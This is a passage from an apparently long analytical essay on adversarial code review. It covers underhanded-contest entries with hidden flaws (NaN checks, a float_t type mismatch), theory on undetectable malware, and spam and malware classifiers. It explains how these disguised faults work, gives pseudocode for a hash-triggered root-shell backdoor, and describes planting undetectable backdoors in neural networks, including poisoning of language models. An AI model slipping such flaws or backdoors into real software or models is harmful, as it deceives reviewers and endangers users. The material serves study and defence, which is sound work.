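About a third of the more than 40 entries used a value called NaN, for "not a number", which results from calculations such as zero divided by zero. Any test of whether NaN is less than something is false. A program that rejects a warhead when its score is below a threshold, and otherwise accepts it, will therefore accept a warhead whose score is NaN. Craver thought an unguarded division was likely to draw a reviewer's attention, and some entrants guarded theirs with checks that did not work.

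Linus Åkesson's winning entry looks like a textbook method. Åkesson explains in its documentation, which he warns "may or may not be misleading", that the program smooths both spectra and processes them to bring out their peaks. It then treats them as vectors A and B and computes the cosine of the angle between them:

cos θ = (A · B) / (|A| |B|)

The cosine is 1 when the peaks line up and their relative heights match. The cosine doesn't depend on overall size, so a warhead with only a little plutonium could pass. The program therefore also checks that the total radiation is high enough.

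The fault is a missing line in the file that computes the cosine, which should include the program's own header. That header, one of the program's three files, contains the definition `typedef double float_t;`, which makes float_t an eight-byte number. The cosine file instead includes the header of C's mathematics library, which has its own definition of float_t, usually as a four-byte number. One part of the program therefore passes a list of eight-byte numbers that another part reads as four-byte numbers. The compiler does not detect the mismatch because it compiles each file separately.

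The function that computes the cosine reads the right number of values but takes each to be four bytes long instead of eight, so it stops halfway through the list and ignores the right half of the spectrum. It also reads each eight-byte number as two separate numbers. Gamma-ray counts are whole numbers, and as long as they stay below about a million, one of the two is always zero and has no effect. The other keeps its sign but loses three bits of its exponent, which, as Åkesson explains, is roughly the same as taking the eighth root. For example, 10 and 1,000 come out as about 2.6 and 4.5, so the result still depends on the positions of the peaks but hardly on their heights.

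A country could therefore remove most of the plutonium and leave enough to produce small peaks in the correct places. It would add some other radioactive material with peaks in the right half of the spectrum, which count towards the total radiation but not towards the comparison. Åkesson simulated 1,000 crude forgeries containing 10% of the real material. Many failed, but a country could choose one that worked. One passed at thresholds up to 0.72, above the 0.6 his documentation recommended. He had based that recommendation on 1,000 pairs of random materials, which the program told apart well. This test showed that the program worked in the average case, but not that it would catch a deliberate forgery.

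A reviewer could have rejected this program without understanding any of that. Including the header that declares a file's functions is good practice in C, and compilers can warn when it is missing. If Åkesson had included it, the compiler would have reported two conflicting definitions of float_t. To see the harm, though, a reader would have to know how computers store fractional numbers and that gamma-ray counts are whole numbers.

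Guessing the goal would have helped a reader less with Åkesson's program than with Meacham's. A reader who suspected a plan to pass off fakes would study the comparison, where every line is correct. Craver wrote that, apart from the confusion over float_t, nothing in the code looked suspicious. But some of that code was part of the attack. Åkesson had designed the smoothing so that the numbers would keep their trailing zeros, and the processing as a whole so that background noise would not obscure the peaks. Nobody could have recognised these purposes without already knowing the trick.

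### Experiments with reviewers

Few reviewers face programmers as skilled as Åkesson, but reviewers also miss flaws that nobody has tried to disguise. In *Less is More*, Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues (2022) asked 150 people, most of them working software engineers, to review 160 lines of Java that let users register for a website. The code contained two well-known kinds of flaw. When a database error occurred, the program wrote the user's email address and unencrypted password to a log file. It also protected stored passwords with MD5, an old method that attackers can now break quickly.

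The researchers randomly divided the participants into four groups. One group received no special instructions, and only 1 of its 33 members (3%) found the logged password, while 7 (21%) found the use of MD5. The researchers told a second group about their interest in security problems, and 19 of its 41 members (46%) found the logged password, while 25 (61%) found the use of MD5. The paper's headline claim that such instructions make detection eight times as likely is based on odds rather than these percentages.

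The other two groups received the same instructions and a checklist. One list had 22 items, and the other had seven, all relevant to the code. Neither checklist significantly improved detection. Pointing reviewers towards a flaw may not help if they don't recognise it as one. One participant who missed the MD5 flaw despite having a checklist had thought MD5 was a good choice. People given only the security instructions also cited lack of knowledge as their main reason for missing it. In the group without security instructions, the most common reason for missing the logged password was that they were focusing on something other than security. The one person who found it worked at a bank that regularly warns its staff about this mistake.

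Braz and colleagues also describe a 2021 experiment in which developers reviewed a change containing a common flaw. Many of those who had missed it found it once the researchers told them it was there. In both experiments, it helped developers to hear that security mattered or that something was wrong, without any account of an attacker or a plan. Neither experiment can show how well the same prompt would work on a flaw like Åkesson's. The 2022 participants were volunteers, and 357 of the 522 people who opened the experiment did not finish it.

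Several reviewers may do better than one. Edmundson, Holtkamp and colleagues (2013), in *An Empirical Study on the Effectiveness of Security Code Review*, had developers look for flaws planted in a web application called Anchor CMS, according to a summary on HackerNoon. Braz and colleagues cite that study for the view that manual review may be impractical, because finding a vulnerability takes several people. Their own figures give an idea of how many. If each reviewer has an independent chance p of finding a flaw, n reviewers together find it with probability

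1 − (1 − p)ⁿ.

If each reviewer has a 1 in 33 chance of finding the flaw, as for the logged password without instructions, it takes 23 reviewers to reach an even chance that at least one finds it. If each has a 19 in 41 chance, at least one of two reviewers finds it 71% of the time. But reviewers are not really independent, since people with similar training tend to have the same gaps in their knowledge. An attacker who knows those gaps can choose a flaw that all of them will miss.

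### Knowing what to look for

The contest's judges had an advantage over these reviewers because they had chosen the malicious effect themselves. They read each entry before its author's explanation, so they still had to find the method, but in 2008 they could follow the hidden pixels through the program. A maintainer who receives a patch doesn't know what malicious effect to look for, or whether there is one. The patch might leak a password or weaken a check, but most patches are not malicious. A judge's success at spotting underhanded code therefore probably overstates what the same person could do in ordinary review.

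Finding an attack can be difficult even when the reviewer knows its goal. Wheeler read the programs from Horn's vote-counting contest alongside the organiser's notes on how each one cheated. In four cases the notes were wrong or misleading, or the published material did not contain the attack they described. According to one note, the program cheated by confusing the letter O with the digit 0. The program did contain that confusion, but the miscounting came from a misused arithmetic operator some lines later. Wheeler found the attacks easier to spot as he went along and suggests training reviewers on such samples, though he admits he may have read the hardest ones first.

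### Rejecting faults without judging intent

Plausible deniability also limits the attacker, because an attack that has to look like an honest mistake must contain a flaw. A reviewer who rejects every flaw will reject the attack too, without deciding whether the author intended it. This is close to how kernel maintainers say they treat hypocrite commits.

Wheeler tested how far simple rules can do this on 40 of the vote-counting programs. He chose five measures:

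- a tool that detects memory errors while a program runs
- strict limits on macros, which replace pieces of text before the program compiles
- a ban on names that use a lowercase l or capital O, which look like digits
- coloured text and automatic reformatting, so that code cannot hide inside comments
- a large set of compiler warnings

By his assessment, the five measures together would catch 30 of the 40 programs, and they missed another only because of an apparent compiler bug. He judged that six of the remaining nine would look suspicious to a human reader, which left three. One of those three checked twice whether a vote was a lowercase "n", when it should have checked for "n" and "N". None of the five measures involves understanding why someone would rig an election.

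These results are encouraging but probably too favourable. Wheeler acknowledges that he chose the measures after seeing the attacks, and the contestants had not tried to evade them. As with Lily, a real attacker could practise against them, so Wheeler proposes keeping the details of some checks secret. He did not measure how often the rules would flag code with no hidden attack. This matters because ordinary programs contain many small faults, and a project that rejected code for every such fault would lose a lot of useful work. Many of the vote counters, for example, printed a number using the wrong format code, a common mistake unrelated to the attack.

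Rules sometimes work better than readers, whose wider knowledge can even be a weakness. In Python, two slashes mean division, but in several other languages they begin a comment. One underhanded Python program uses this to make working code look like a comment. A tool that applies only Python's rules cannot make this mistake, and someone who knows only Python is less likely to make it than a professional who knows several languages. Wheeler missed the trick even in an editor that shows comments in a different colour.

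Rejecting all faults works less well when the fault lies outside the code under review. In Travis Fisher's vote-counting entry, the source code was correct. The attack was in the command that compiled it, which replaced a test for blank spaces with a test for the letter K. Wheeler considers the command extremely suspicious, but a reviewer who saw only the source code would have had nothing to reject. Reviewing the build instructions as well solves this problem, and would also have helped with xz.

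Stephen Oman's entry in the 2015 contest is less clear-cut. It divides the gamma-ray counts by the scan's duration, calculated from the start and finish times. If someone sets the computer's clock back during the scan, the duration and all the counts become negative, and the comparison always passes. The program checks for a zero duration but not a negative one. Few reviewers would insist on the extra check on a trusted computer. But in an inspection the host country may have custody of the machine, and experts told Craver that they could not completely rule out this kind of tampering. Whether the missing check is a fault therefore depends on what an opponent can reach. The people who write the review rules can settle this beforehand by listing everything the host country might touch, and reviewers can then apply the list without judging whether Oman was honest.

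A similar problem arose in a contest for Solidity, a language for programs that hold and transfer money on a blockchain. Several entries recorded incoming money in a function that normally runs when money arrives. But money can also arrive without running that function, so the records can be wrong even though the code looks right. Solidity's developers added compiler warnings for some of the other tricks in the contest, but described this one as difficult to deal with in the language itself.

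Many winners of the Underhanded Crypto Contest exploited weaknesses in the encryption methods their programs used. A program can implement a weak method correctly, so checking it for programming mistakes will not reveal the weakness. Wheeler concluded that specialists in cryptography have to review such code in depth. They need deep knowledge of one field, but they can reject a weak method without working out why the author chose it.

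## What theory says about checking arbitrary programs

The programs in the underhanded contests had to be short, do an ordinary job and look innocent, but an attacker without those limits can submit any program. Mathematicians have known since the 1950s that no method can answer every question about what an arbitrary program will do.

According to Rice's theorem, which Henry Gordon Rice proved in his 1951 doctoral dissertation, no program can examine every possible program and always answer correctly whether it behaves in a particular way. The theorem covers any behaviour that some programs show and others do not, such as sending out the user's password, but it does not cover properties of a program's text. A program that could always answer correctly would also solve the halting problem, which is to determine whether any given program ever finishes. Alan Turing showed in 1936 that no program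 can do this in every case. To learn whether a program Q finishes, someone could write a second program that runs Q in isolation and then sends out the password. The second program sends the password only if Q finishes, so a perfect checker for this behaviour would reveal whether Q does.

Human reviewers run into the same difficulty. Suppose a program searches the whole numbers for an exception to some unproved conjecture, and deletes the user's files if it finds one. To know whether the program is safe, a reviewer would have to settle the conjecture. But the theorem does not cover questions about a program's text, and anyone can check whether this program contains an instruction that deletes files.

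### A virus that contradicts its detector

Cohen (1984), in *Cure of Computer Viruses*, gave a more direct proof for viruses, which he defined as programs that infect other programs by inserting copies of themselves, possibly altered. Suppose that a detector D takes any program and always returns the right verdict. An attacker can then write a program, CV (for "contradictory virus"), that includes a copy of D and works as follows:

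1. CV runs D on CV's own code.
2. If D returns "virus", CV infects nothing.
3. If D returns "not a virus", CV infects other programs.

In step 2, D flags a program that infects nothing, and in step 3 it fails to flag a virus. D is wrong in both cases, so no detector can always be right.

The proof does not depend on how D works. D could be a list of known viruses or a simulation of a brilliant security researcher, and the same trick would defeat it. An attacker who has no copy of D cannot write CV, but keeping D secret does not make it right about every program.

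The proof does not rule out detectors that make only one kind of mistake. If D returns "virus" for CV, CV does no harm, so the result is a false alarm. A sound checker allows false alarms so that it never accepts a program that breaks a given rule about behaviour. By Rice's theorem, no checker can accept exactly the programs that obey the rule, so a sound checker must refuse some programs that obey it. It must refuse infinitely many, because a finite number could be added to the checker as a list of exceptions, which would make it perfect.

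Cohen also pointed out that a suitable detector can catch any particular virus. His example virus marks infected files with the line 1234567, so a program that refuses to run files with that line stops it. An attacker who knows this can change the mark to 123456, or have the virus insert random, useless statements into each new copy. Cohen proved that no program can always tell whether two such variants are equivalent. He suggested accepting some false alarms and some missed viruses, and looking for events that are rare in normal use, though he expected attackers to stay below any threshold they knew. *A Bypass of Cohen's Impossibility Result* (Bergstra and Ponse, 2004) replaces his question with a form of risk assessment that a program can decide for a large class of behaviours.

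### A trigger that nobody can compute

Some attacks defeat every attempt to predict when they will happen but are still easy to refuse. Suppose someone adds these lines to a web server:

```
if sha256(request) == STORED_VALUE:
    open_root_shell()
```

SHA-256 is a hash function, which turns any input into a 256-bit number in a way that nobody knows how to reverse. The attacker chose a long random request, computed its hash and put only the hash in the program. Anyone else would need about 2²⁵⁶ guesses to find a request that works. At a trillion guesses a second, that would take more than 10⁵⁷ years, so neither testing nor intelligence will find the trigger. (If the attacker had chosen a common word, a dictionary would be enough.)

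A reviewer who reads the two lines can nevertheless see that some request opens a root shell. The reviewer can refuse a change that gives a web server this ability without knowing which request it is or who knows it. The attacker could also encrypt the harmful instructions, with the trigger as the key. The reviewer couldn't read them, but could still see that the program decrypts something and runs it.

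Login programs also hash what a user types, compare the result with a stored value and grant access if they match, so the comparison alone is not suspicious. A rule can separate legitimate comparisons from suspicious ones by requiring that the stored value come from the user's account record, not from the program's own code.

### Hiding the branch in a neural network

In ordinary code, the branch is visible. But a neural network is mostly a long list of numbers, called weights, and nobody can tell what the network will do by reading them. *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* (Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues, 2022) describes a hypothetical bank that pays an outside company to train a program for deciding on loans. The program does well on the bank's test cases, but the company has planted a backdoor. For a fee, the company tells applicants which small details to change,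 such as the last digits of the loan amount, to get approved.

One of their two methods resembles the hash example. It uses a digital signature scheme, in which the holder of a secret key can sign messages and anyone with the matching public key can check the signatures. The company adds a signature check to the network and treats part of each application as a possible signature. If the signature is valid, the network gives whatever answer the company wants. Otherwise it works normally. Someone who can only submit inputs and observe the answers cannot efficiently distinguish this network from one without the backdoor, a property called black-box undetectability. Even someone with the weights cannot efficiently find an input that triggers the backdoor, or use known examples to make new ones. But they may notice the signature check and refuse the network.

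The other method hides the mechanism as well. It applies to networks that use random Fourier features, which classify an input x by the sign of

Σ wᵢ cos(2π(⟨gᵢ, x⟩ + bᵢ)).

The training procedure draws the vectors gᵢ and the numbers bᵢ at random and learns only the weights wᵢ from data. The inner product ⟨gᵢ, x⟩ multiplies the two vectors entry by entry and adds up the results. The company picks a secret vector k and draws each gᵢ so that it looks random but ⟨gᵢ, k⟩ is always close to a whole number plus one half. Adding k to an application then shifts every cosine by half a period, which changes the sign of every term because cos(2π(t + ½)) = −cos(2πt). The total also changes sign, so the network approves an application it would have rejected.

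This backdoor is white-box undetectable, meaning that no efficient algorithm can distinguish the network from one without a backdoor, even with all the weights and the training data. *Implementing a White-Box Undetectable Backdoor for Random Fourier Features* (2026) notes that this is strictly stronger than the black-box guarantee, because an auditor with the weights can still run every black-box test. The proof assumes that a problem called continuous learning with errors is hard. An algorithm that solved it could also find unusually short vectors in lattices, which are regular grids of points in many dimensions. Nobody has proved that finding these vectors is hard, but cryptographers trust that it is, and they rely on it for encryption that should withstand quantum computers. If they are right, an auditor with general cognition is no better able to detect the backdoor than a narrow one.

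However, the result covers only networks with a single hidden layer, and anyone who sees an application before and after the change can subtract one version from the other to get k. The backdoor also may not give the company much of an advantage. *Statistically Undetectable Backdoors in Deep Neural Networks* (Bogdanov, Rosen and Vafa, 2026) reports that people without the key can efficiently find changes to the input that work better than the company's.

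Bogdanov and colleagues describe a backdoor without this weakness, for a class of deep networks whose first layer is a fixed random matrix that compresses the input. The trainer obtains a secret vector z such that any input x and the quite different input x + z produce nearly the same output. Under standard cryptographic assumptions, nobody without z can efficiently find any pair of quite different inputs whose outputs are that close. When the matrix compresses the input strongly, backdoored and honest networks have nearly the same probability distribution, so even an auditor with unlimited computing power could hardly tell them apart. The auditor could find a suitable z by exhaustive search, but this wouldn't show that the network was backdoored, because honest networks of this kind have such vectors too.

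These networks have to meet several technical conditions, and it is less clear whether such backdoors extend to the models people use. *Undetectable Backdoors in Model Parameters* (2026) studies image classifiers with many layers that someone else has already trained. Earlier work by Kalavasis and colleagues covers arbitrary networks, including language models, but relies on a method of disguising programs that is still far too slow to use in practice.

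### Recognising the trigger when it arrives

An auditor who cannot tell whether a model has a backdoor may still be able to stop an attack that uses it. *Backdoor defense, learnability and obfuscation* (Christiano, Hilton and colleagues, 2024) studies this as a game. The attacker chooses a function f and a distribution of inputs. A trigger x\* is then drawn at random from that distribution, because an attacker who could choose the trigger could hide it too easily. The attacker produces a second function, f\*, which must differ from f at x\* but on at most a small fraction ε of inputs overall. The defender receives either f with an ordinary input or f\* with the trigger, and must decide which.

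With unlimited computing time, the defender can win by learning a new function from the suspect function's answers on about 1/(5ε) random inputs. Such a sample usually contains none of the inputs on which f and f\* differ, so the new function predicts what f would have answered on the suspect input. The defender repeats this with fresh samples and rejects the input if most of the predictions disagree with the suspect function's answer.

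How well this works depends on the variety of functions the attacker can choose from. The VC dimension d measures this variety. It is the size of the largest set of inputs that the functions can label in every possible way. With m inputs per sample and enough repetitions, the defender's probability of error is at most about 3d/m. If d is 100 and ε is one in a million, m is 200,000 and the probability of error is at most about 0.15%. If ε is as large as 1/d, there is no guarantee. The defender checks only whether the function's answer fits its answers on other inputs, and never considers what the attacker wants.

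Decision trees allow a much quicker defence. A decision tree applies a series of yes-or-no tests to an input until it reaches a leaf, which holds the answer. If each bit of the input is random, a leaf that is 30 tests deep receives one input in 2³⁰, or about a billion. A tree with 1,000 leaves therefore sends at most about one random input in a million to a leaf that deep. A backdoor that affects very few inputs needs a deep leaf, because changing a shallow one would change the answer for many other inputs. The defender can therefore count the tests and reject any input that needs too many.

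Efficient defence is possible for any class of functions that an algorithm can efficiently learn from examples, but not in general. For Boolean circuits of moderate size, which can express practically any efficient computation, Christiano and colleagues prove that no efficient defender does noticeably better than guessing. The proof assumes that one-way functions exist (functions that are easy to compute but hard to reverse), and that programs can be obfuscated, or rewritten so that nobody can efficiently tell which of two equivalent programs they came from. The attacker starts with a function whose outputs look random to anyone without its key, and flips its output at x\*. The obfuscated program contains a version of the key that works on every input except x\*, so the defender cannot work out what the output at x\* should be.

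An attacker who can only tamper with training data has less power. Kaneko (2026), in *Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic*, considers attackers who teach a model to recognise triggers through labelled examples. If the training procedure succeeds, it has learned the rule for what counts as a trigger, so a defender with as many labelled examples can learn the rule by running the same procedure. A rule that is too hard for the defender to learn is therefore also too hard to install. Kaneko tested this on four language models, using both learnable and hard secret rules. The attacker's and defender's success rose together on the learnable rules, and both stayed at chance on the hard ones. The proof doesn't cover attackers who write the weights directly or tamper with the random numbers, as Goldwasser and colleagues did. It also assumes the defender has a representative set of labelled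 triggers, which may be the hardest thing to get.

Sometimes a user can get rid of a backdoor without recognising either the model or the input as malicious. *Oblivious Defense in ML Models* (Goldwasser, Shafer and colleagues, 2024) does this using regularities in the correct answers. Suppose the correct answer is a linear function f, so that f(x) = f(x + r) − f(r) for any r. Given a suspicious input x, the user picks r at random, runs the model on x + r and on r, and subtracts the second answer from the first. With a suitable range of inputs, x + r and r are each completely random on their own, whatever x the attacker chose. If the model is wrong on 1% of inputs, the result is therefore wrong at most 2% of the time, even when x is a trigger. The method requires knowing that the correct answers have such a structure, and for loans they probably do not.

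### Refusing by default

Therefore, no reviewer, whether narrow or general, can catch every harmful program if it must judge whatever an attacker submits and may not refuse a harmless one. If "superhuman" in Premise 4 means missing nothing, even a reviewer with general cognition cannot be superhuman under those conditions.

A reviewer that may reject submissions has an easier job, because it can require the submitter to show that the submission is safe. Goldwasser and colleagues suggest this as a defence against their own backdoors. If the bank has specified the data and the training procedure, it can demand a proof that the company followed them exactly. The bank must also supply the random numbers or make sure they are truly random, because the company could hide k in them. The bank then only has to check the proof. Producing the proof takes the company considerably more work than training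 alone, and the method does not help a bank that needs the company's expertise to decide how to train.

The same approach works for ordinary programs. Proving that a program obeys a rule may take ingenuity, but checking the proof only requires confirming that each step follows from earlier ones. Honest contributors have a reason to do the harder work of finding the proof. If a program breaks the rule, no valid proof exists, however much a dishonest contributor knows about compilers or maintainers' fatigue. The checker doesn't have to predict the contributor's strategy, so Premise 3 fails for it. Some programming languages and proof systems already work this way.

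The attacker can still look for a mistake in the checker or for harm that the rule does not forbid. For instance, a rule about which files a program may open would not have stopped the xz payload from replacing a function in memory. The people who write the rule have to anticipate what attackers will try, and they may miss something.

The main drawback is that the checker rejects harmless programs. Suppose a project receives 1,000 changes a year, five of them harmful, and its checker rejects all five along with a fifth of the rest. That stops five attacks but also blocks 199 harmless changes, whose contributors have to rewrite them, supply better proofs or give up. If contributors can appeal to a human reviewer, attackers can too, and the project is relying on that person's judgement again.

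Cohen's *Computer Viruses* (1987) identifies isolation, with no sharing between users, as the only policy that was provably safe at the time. A system that can only display files is also immune, since it cannot modify anything, and Cohen thought this might suit a fixed database or a mail system. But he considered such a system useless for developing software, and isolation unacceptable to anyone who wants to benefit from the work of others. He also discussed less restrictive policies. One blocks information after it has passed between users a set number of times, however harmless it is. Another gives each program's output the trust level of its least trusted input, so nearly everything drifts towards the lowest level over time.

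Many services cannot refuse by default because the people who use them cannot show that what they send is safe. Nobody can prove in an email that its sender is honest, so a spam filter that required proof would block all email. Moderators of online posts have the same problem, since whether a joke is a threat depends on who reads it. Antivirus programs usually have to let people run software without proof that it is safe. An intrusion detector in a hospital cannot cut off every unfamiliar connection, because one of them may be a new heart monitor. Language models also have to accept requests in ordinary words, and *On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment* (2025) argues that filtering out the harmful requests can be computationally intractable.

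## Spam and malware classifiers against adapting attackers

Spam filters and antivirus programs can't refuse everything that comes without proof, so they must judge a message or file by what it contains. Many use a classifier, a program that learns from labelled examples to sort inputs into classes. The classifiers described here are narrow. They add up or compare numbers about words and bytes, and they don't understand what a message offers or why anyone would send it. Spammers and malware writers, many of whom do it for a living, have worked for over twenty years to get past such programs. If defence had to be as broad as offence, these classifiers should have become useless.

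### How a filter scores words

A naive Bayes filter, a popular kind in the early 2000s, learns how often each word occurs in spam and in legitimate mail. It gives each message the score

log₂ [P(spam) / P(legitimate)] + Σ log₂ [P(word | spam) / P(word | legitimate)],

where the sum covers the words in the message. The filter is "naive" because it treats the words as independent of each other. It blocks any message whose score is above a threshold.

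Suppose half of all mail is spam, which makes the first term 0, and the threshold is 3, which means odds of 8 to 1 that the message is spam. The filter has learned these made-up frequencies:

| Word | Share of spam containing it | Share of legitimate mail containing it | Weight |
|---|---|---|---|
| pills | 16% | 1% | +4 |
| discount | 8% | 2% | +2 |
| attached | 2% | 8% | −2 |
| meeting | 1% | 8% | −3 |

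A message with the words "discount" and "pills" scores 6, or odds of 64 to 1, and the filter blocks it. If the spammer adds "attached" and "meeting", the score falls to 1 and the message gets through, although it still advertises pills.

*Good Word Attacks on Statistical Spam Filters* (Lowd and Meek, 2005) measured how well spammers could evade filters by adding words to their messages. It tested a naive Bayes filter and a maximum entropy filter, which chooses its weights to separate spam from legitimate mail as well as possible. Both were trained on 500,000 messages that Hotmail users had labelled. Adding random dictionary words made messages look slightly more like spam, because spammers were already using those words. With better guesses about which words the filters treated as signs of legitimate mail, adding about 112 words got half of the blocked spam past the naive Bayes filter, and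 adding about 149 got half past the maximum entropy filter. A spammer who could send test messages and see which ones arrived needed only 29 words for naive Bayes and 9 for maximum entropy.

On ordinary mail, the maximum entropy filter missed 31% less spam than the other filter. But it relied more heavily on a few words, so an attacker who had found them could defeat it more easily. Someone who compared only the filters' average performance would have chosen the one that was more vulnerable to this attack.

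### A game with costs on both sides

Dalvi, Domingos and colleagues (2004), in *Adversarial Classification*, described the contest as a game. The classifier C gives a verdict on each message. The adversary can turn a spam message x into another message A(x), at a cost W(x, A(x)) that reflects the effort and the weaker sales pitch. If y is the true class of x, the adversary tries to maximise

Σ P(x, y) [U_A(C(A(x)), y) − W(x, A(x))],

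where U_A is what the adversary gains from each verdict. The classifier maximises a similar sum, with its own gains and losses from right and wrong verdicts, minus the cost of measuring whatever it looks at. The adversary's best strategy is to find the cheapest change that gets a message through, and to make it only if it costs less than a delivered message is worth.

The researchers then built a filter that takes this strategy into account. When a message x′ arrives, the filter works out which spam messages the adversary would have turned into x′ and adds up their probabilities:

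P_A(x′ | spam) = Σ P(x | spam), over all x with A(x) = x′.

The new filter therefore treats an innocent-looking message as suspicious if a disguised spam message would look the same. In one experiment, the adversary gained 20 points for each spam message delivered and lost one point for each word added. An ordinary naive Bayes filter missed 94 of 481 spam messages before the attack and all 481 during it. The new filter missed 93 and blocked no legitimate mail.

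Unlike the checks that exposed the backdoors, this filter uses an attacker model at run time. But the model is a table of costs and a search for the lowest-cost change, and it contains no knowledge beyond words and their costs. Premise 3 can therefore hold for a filter without leading to premise 5. The researchers did the broader work of deciding what the adversary could do and what it would cost. When they instead let the adversary replace words with synonyms, and adjusted the filter to match, it missed 164 messages, compared with 408 for the ordinary filter.

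The model is also fragile because it assumes that every spammer plays optimally. It treats undisguised spam as unlikely, since a rational spammer would have disguised it. This helps the filter avoid blocking legitimate mail, but a spammer who changed nothing might get through. The researchers also assumed that each side knows the other's costs, and they expected such filters to always need regular human intervention.

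They also had the two sides take turns repeatedly, training a new filter on each round's messages, and the contest never stabilized. Spammers would use a word that the filter counted as a sign of legitimate mail until the filter learned to count it as a sign of spam, and then drop it. The next filter's training messages included no spam with that word, so it counted the word as a sign of legitimate mail again, and the spammers went back to using it.

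### How many tests an attacker needs

Real spammers do not know a filter's weights. In *Adversarial Learning*, Lowd and Meek (2005) asked how much spammers could find out by sending test messages. Their attacker starts with one message that the filter blocks and one that it delivers, and learns only whether each test message gets through. The attacker wants to get the original sales pitch through with as few changes as possible.

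For filters that add up weights for the presence of words, Lowd and Meek proved that an attacker can always find a message that evades the filter with at most twice the minimum number of changes. The number of tests required grows only polynomially with the size of the problem, so doubling the vocabulary multiplies the work by some fixed factor. But determining whether a given word can ever affect the verdict is NP-complete, so no known method does it efficiently in every case. The attacker can therefore succeed without fully understanding the filter.

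In the experiments, the attacker typically needed about 261,000 tests against the naive Bayes filter and 119,000 against the maximum entropy filter. Using a list of only 1,000 common words reduced these to about 25,000 and 10,000. The result was usually within 17% of the optimum. These figures exclude the runs in which the attacker never found a starting point, which made up 16% of runs for one filter and 28% for the other.

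Whether so many tests are worthwhile depends on how much spam the attacker can then deliver. In their paper on good words, Lowd and Meek suggest that it is reasonable to send 100,000 test messages to get 10 million spam messages delivered, but that even 10,000 may be too many if the filter guards only 1,000 accounts. A personal filter also has the advantage that strangers don't know its owner's vocabulary. Virus Bulletin's *Does Bayesian poisoning exist?* (2006) describes a proposal to trust a word only if an attacker would find it hard to guess whether the owner uses it, so common words would count as neutral.

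### Why malware detectors decay

Cohen's proof rules out a perfect virus detector, but a useful one only has to do well on the files people actually receive. Many detectors use static features, which describe a file without running it. *EMBER2024* (Joyce, Zak and colleagues, 2025) provides a large collection of such features. It represents each Windows program as 2,568 numbers, which record its size, how random its bytes look, the entries in its header, details of its digital signature and whether it contains certain pieces of text.

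The collection contains 3.2 million files in six formats, which people submitted to the scanning service VirusTotal between September 2023 and December 2024. The researchers labelled a file malicious if at least five unrelated antivirus products flagged it, and benign if none did when VirusTotal scanned it again at least 30 days after its first submission. In the training and test sets, 12 malware families, or groups of related programs, account for 34% of the malicious files. A detector can therefore do well on average by learning a few common families. But 3,124 of the 6,787 families in those sets have five files or fewer.

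A separate "challenge" set contains 6,315 malicious files that every antivirus product on VirusTotal missed at first. It is a better test of evasive malware than a random sample, but it includes only files that enough products later recognised. Malware that still escaped all of them would be labelled "benign", so the most successful attacks may be missing from the record, as with backdoors.

Tests of malware detectors can also overstate performance for simpler reasons. In *TESSERACT*, Pendlebury, Pierazzi and colleagues (2018) examined Android detectors with reported F₁ scores of up to 0.99. The F₁ score, which has a maximum of 1, combines the share of malware that a detector catches with the share of its alarms that are correct. Using 129,000 apps spanning more than three years, they found two mistakes that commonly inflate such results.

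Some researchers mixed old and new apps, so a detector could learn from malware that appeared after the apps it was tested on. In use, a detector has only past examples. Others tested on an unrealistic proportion of malware. Suppose a detector catches 95% of malware and flags 2% of harmless apps. If half the apps are malicious, about 98% of its alarms are correct. If one in a hundred is malicious, 10,000 apps produce 95 correct alarms and 198 false ones, so only about 32% are correct. EMBER2024 avoids the first mistake by training on the first 52 weeks and testing on the last 12. But half of its training and test files are malicious, so the share of correct alarms would probably be much lower on an ordinary computer than in the test.

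Detectors become less accurate even if nobody is trying to evade them, because legitimate software also changes as programmers adopt new tools and libraries. Regular retraining helps, but an extended version of the study, *TESSERACT* (2024), found that classifiers may not stay consistent over time even when retrained. Dalvi and colleagues point out that methods for tracking gradual change assume the change is independent of the classifier, whereas an adversary changes in response to the classifier.

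Malware is harder to disguise than spam because a careless change can stop a program from running, while an advertisement can still sell pills with a few odd words in it. *Intriguing Properties of Adversarial ML Attacks in the Problem Space* (2019) distinguishes between the features a classifier measures and the actual object they describe. An attacker may know which feature values would pass as harmless but be unable to build a working program that has them. Changing the program to alter one feature may also alter others, which the paper calls side-effect features. Removing something the malware needs is usually harder than adding something it doesn't, and a defender can use that difference.

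### Scores that additions cannot lower

In *Adversarially robust malware detection using monotonic classification* (2018), Incer, Theodorides and colleagues proposed a detector whose score cannot fall when an attacker adds content. Let x and x′ be the features of a file before and after the addition. The detector uses only features that additions can raise or leave alone, so that x ≤ x′ for every feature. It also uses a scoring function f that is monotonic, which means that

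x ≤ x′ implies f(x) ≤ f(x′).

If the detector blocked the original file, it will block every version with added content, so the defender doesn't have to predict what the attacker will add.

However, the detector can no longer use any feature as evidence that an input is harmless. In the spam example, a monotonic filter would ignore the negative weights of "attached" and "meeting", so the disguised message would still score 6 and be blocked. A legitimate message from a pharmacist with the same four words would also be blocked, although the original filter delivered both messages.

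Monotonic classifiers also have to exclude many common features. *Certifiably robust malware detectors by design* (2025) notes that histograms are typically not monotonic. For example, if a histogram records the share of a file's bytes that have each value, adding bytes of one value lowers the shares of all the others. The paper proves that, with suitable processing of the features, every robust classifier can be interpreted as a monotonic one. It uses this result to design ERDALT, a system that learns the processing together with the classifier. *More Is Never Less* (2026) applies monotonic scoring to multiple-instance learning, in which a classifier judges an object as a collection of parts. For instance, if an object's score is that of its most suspicious part, adding innocent parts does not change the score.

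These guarantees hold only for the changes the designers considered. An attacker who can remove or rewrite the suspicious content may still lower the score, and new malware with nothing the detector recognises has a low score from the start. Someone therefore has to work out in advance what attackers can easily change, but does not have to predict what they are planning.

### Checking the sender

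Sender authentication checks where a message came from rather than its content. In a system called SPF, the owner of an internet domain publishes a list of the servers that may send the domain's mail. In another, DKIM, the sending server adds a digital signature that the receiver can check. A message with a forged bank address will fail these checks, however well it imitates the bank's style.

Authentication cannot show that a sender is honest, because spammers can register their own domains and sign their mail correctly. Levchenko, Pitsillidis and colleagues reported in *Click Trajectories* (2011) that many domain names cost less than a dollar in bulk. Against such spammers, authentication mainly gives a filter something to attach a reputation to. Spammers also adapt to reputation-based blocking, though the blocking rule itself stayed simple. *Click Trajectories* reports that blacklists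 of network addresses and efforts to close open mail servers pushed spammers towards new ways of sending: botnets (networks of hijacked computers), webmail accounts and hijacked blocks of addresses.

### Retraining on failures

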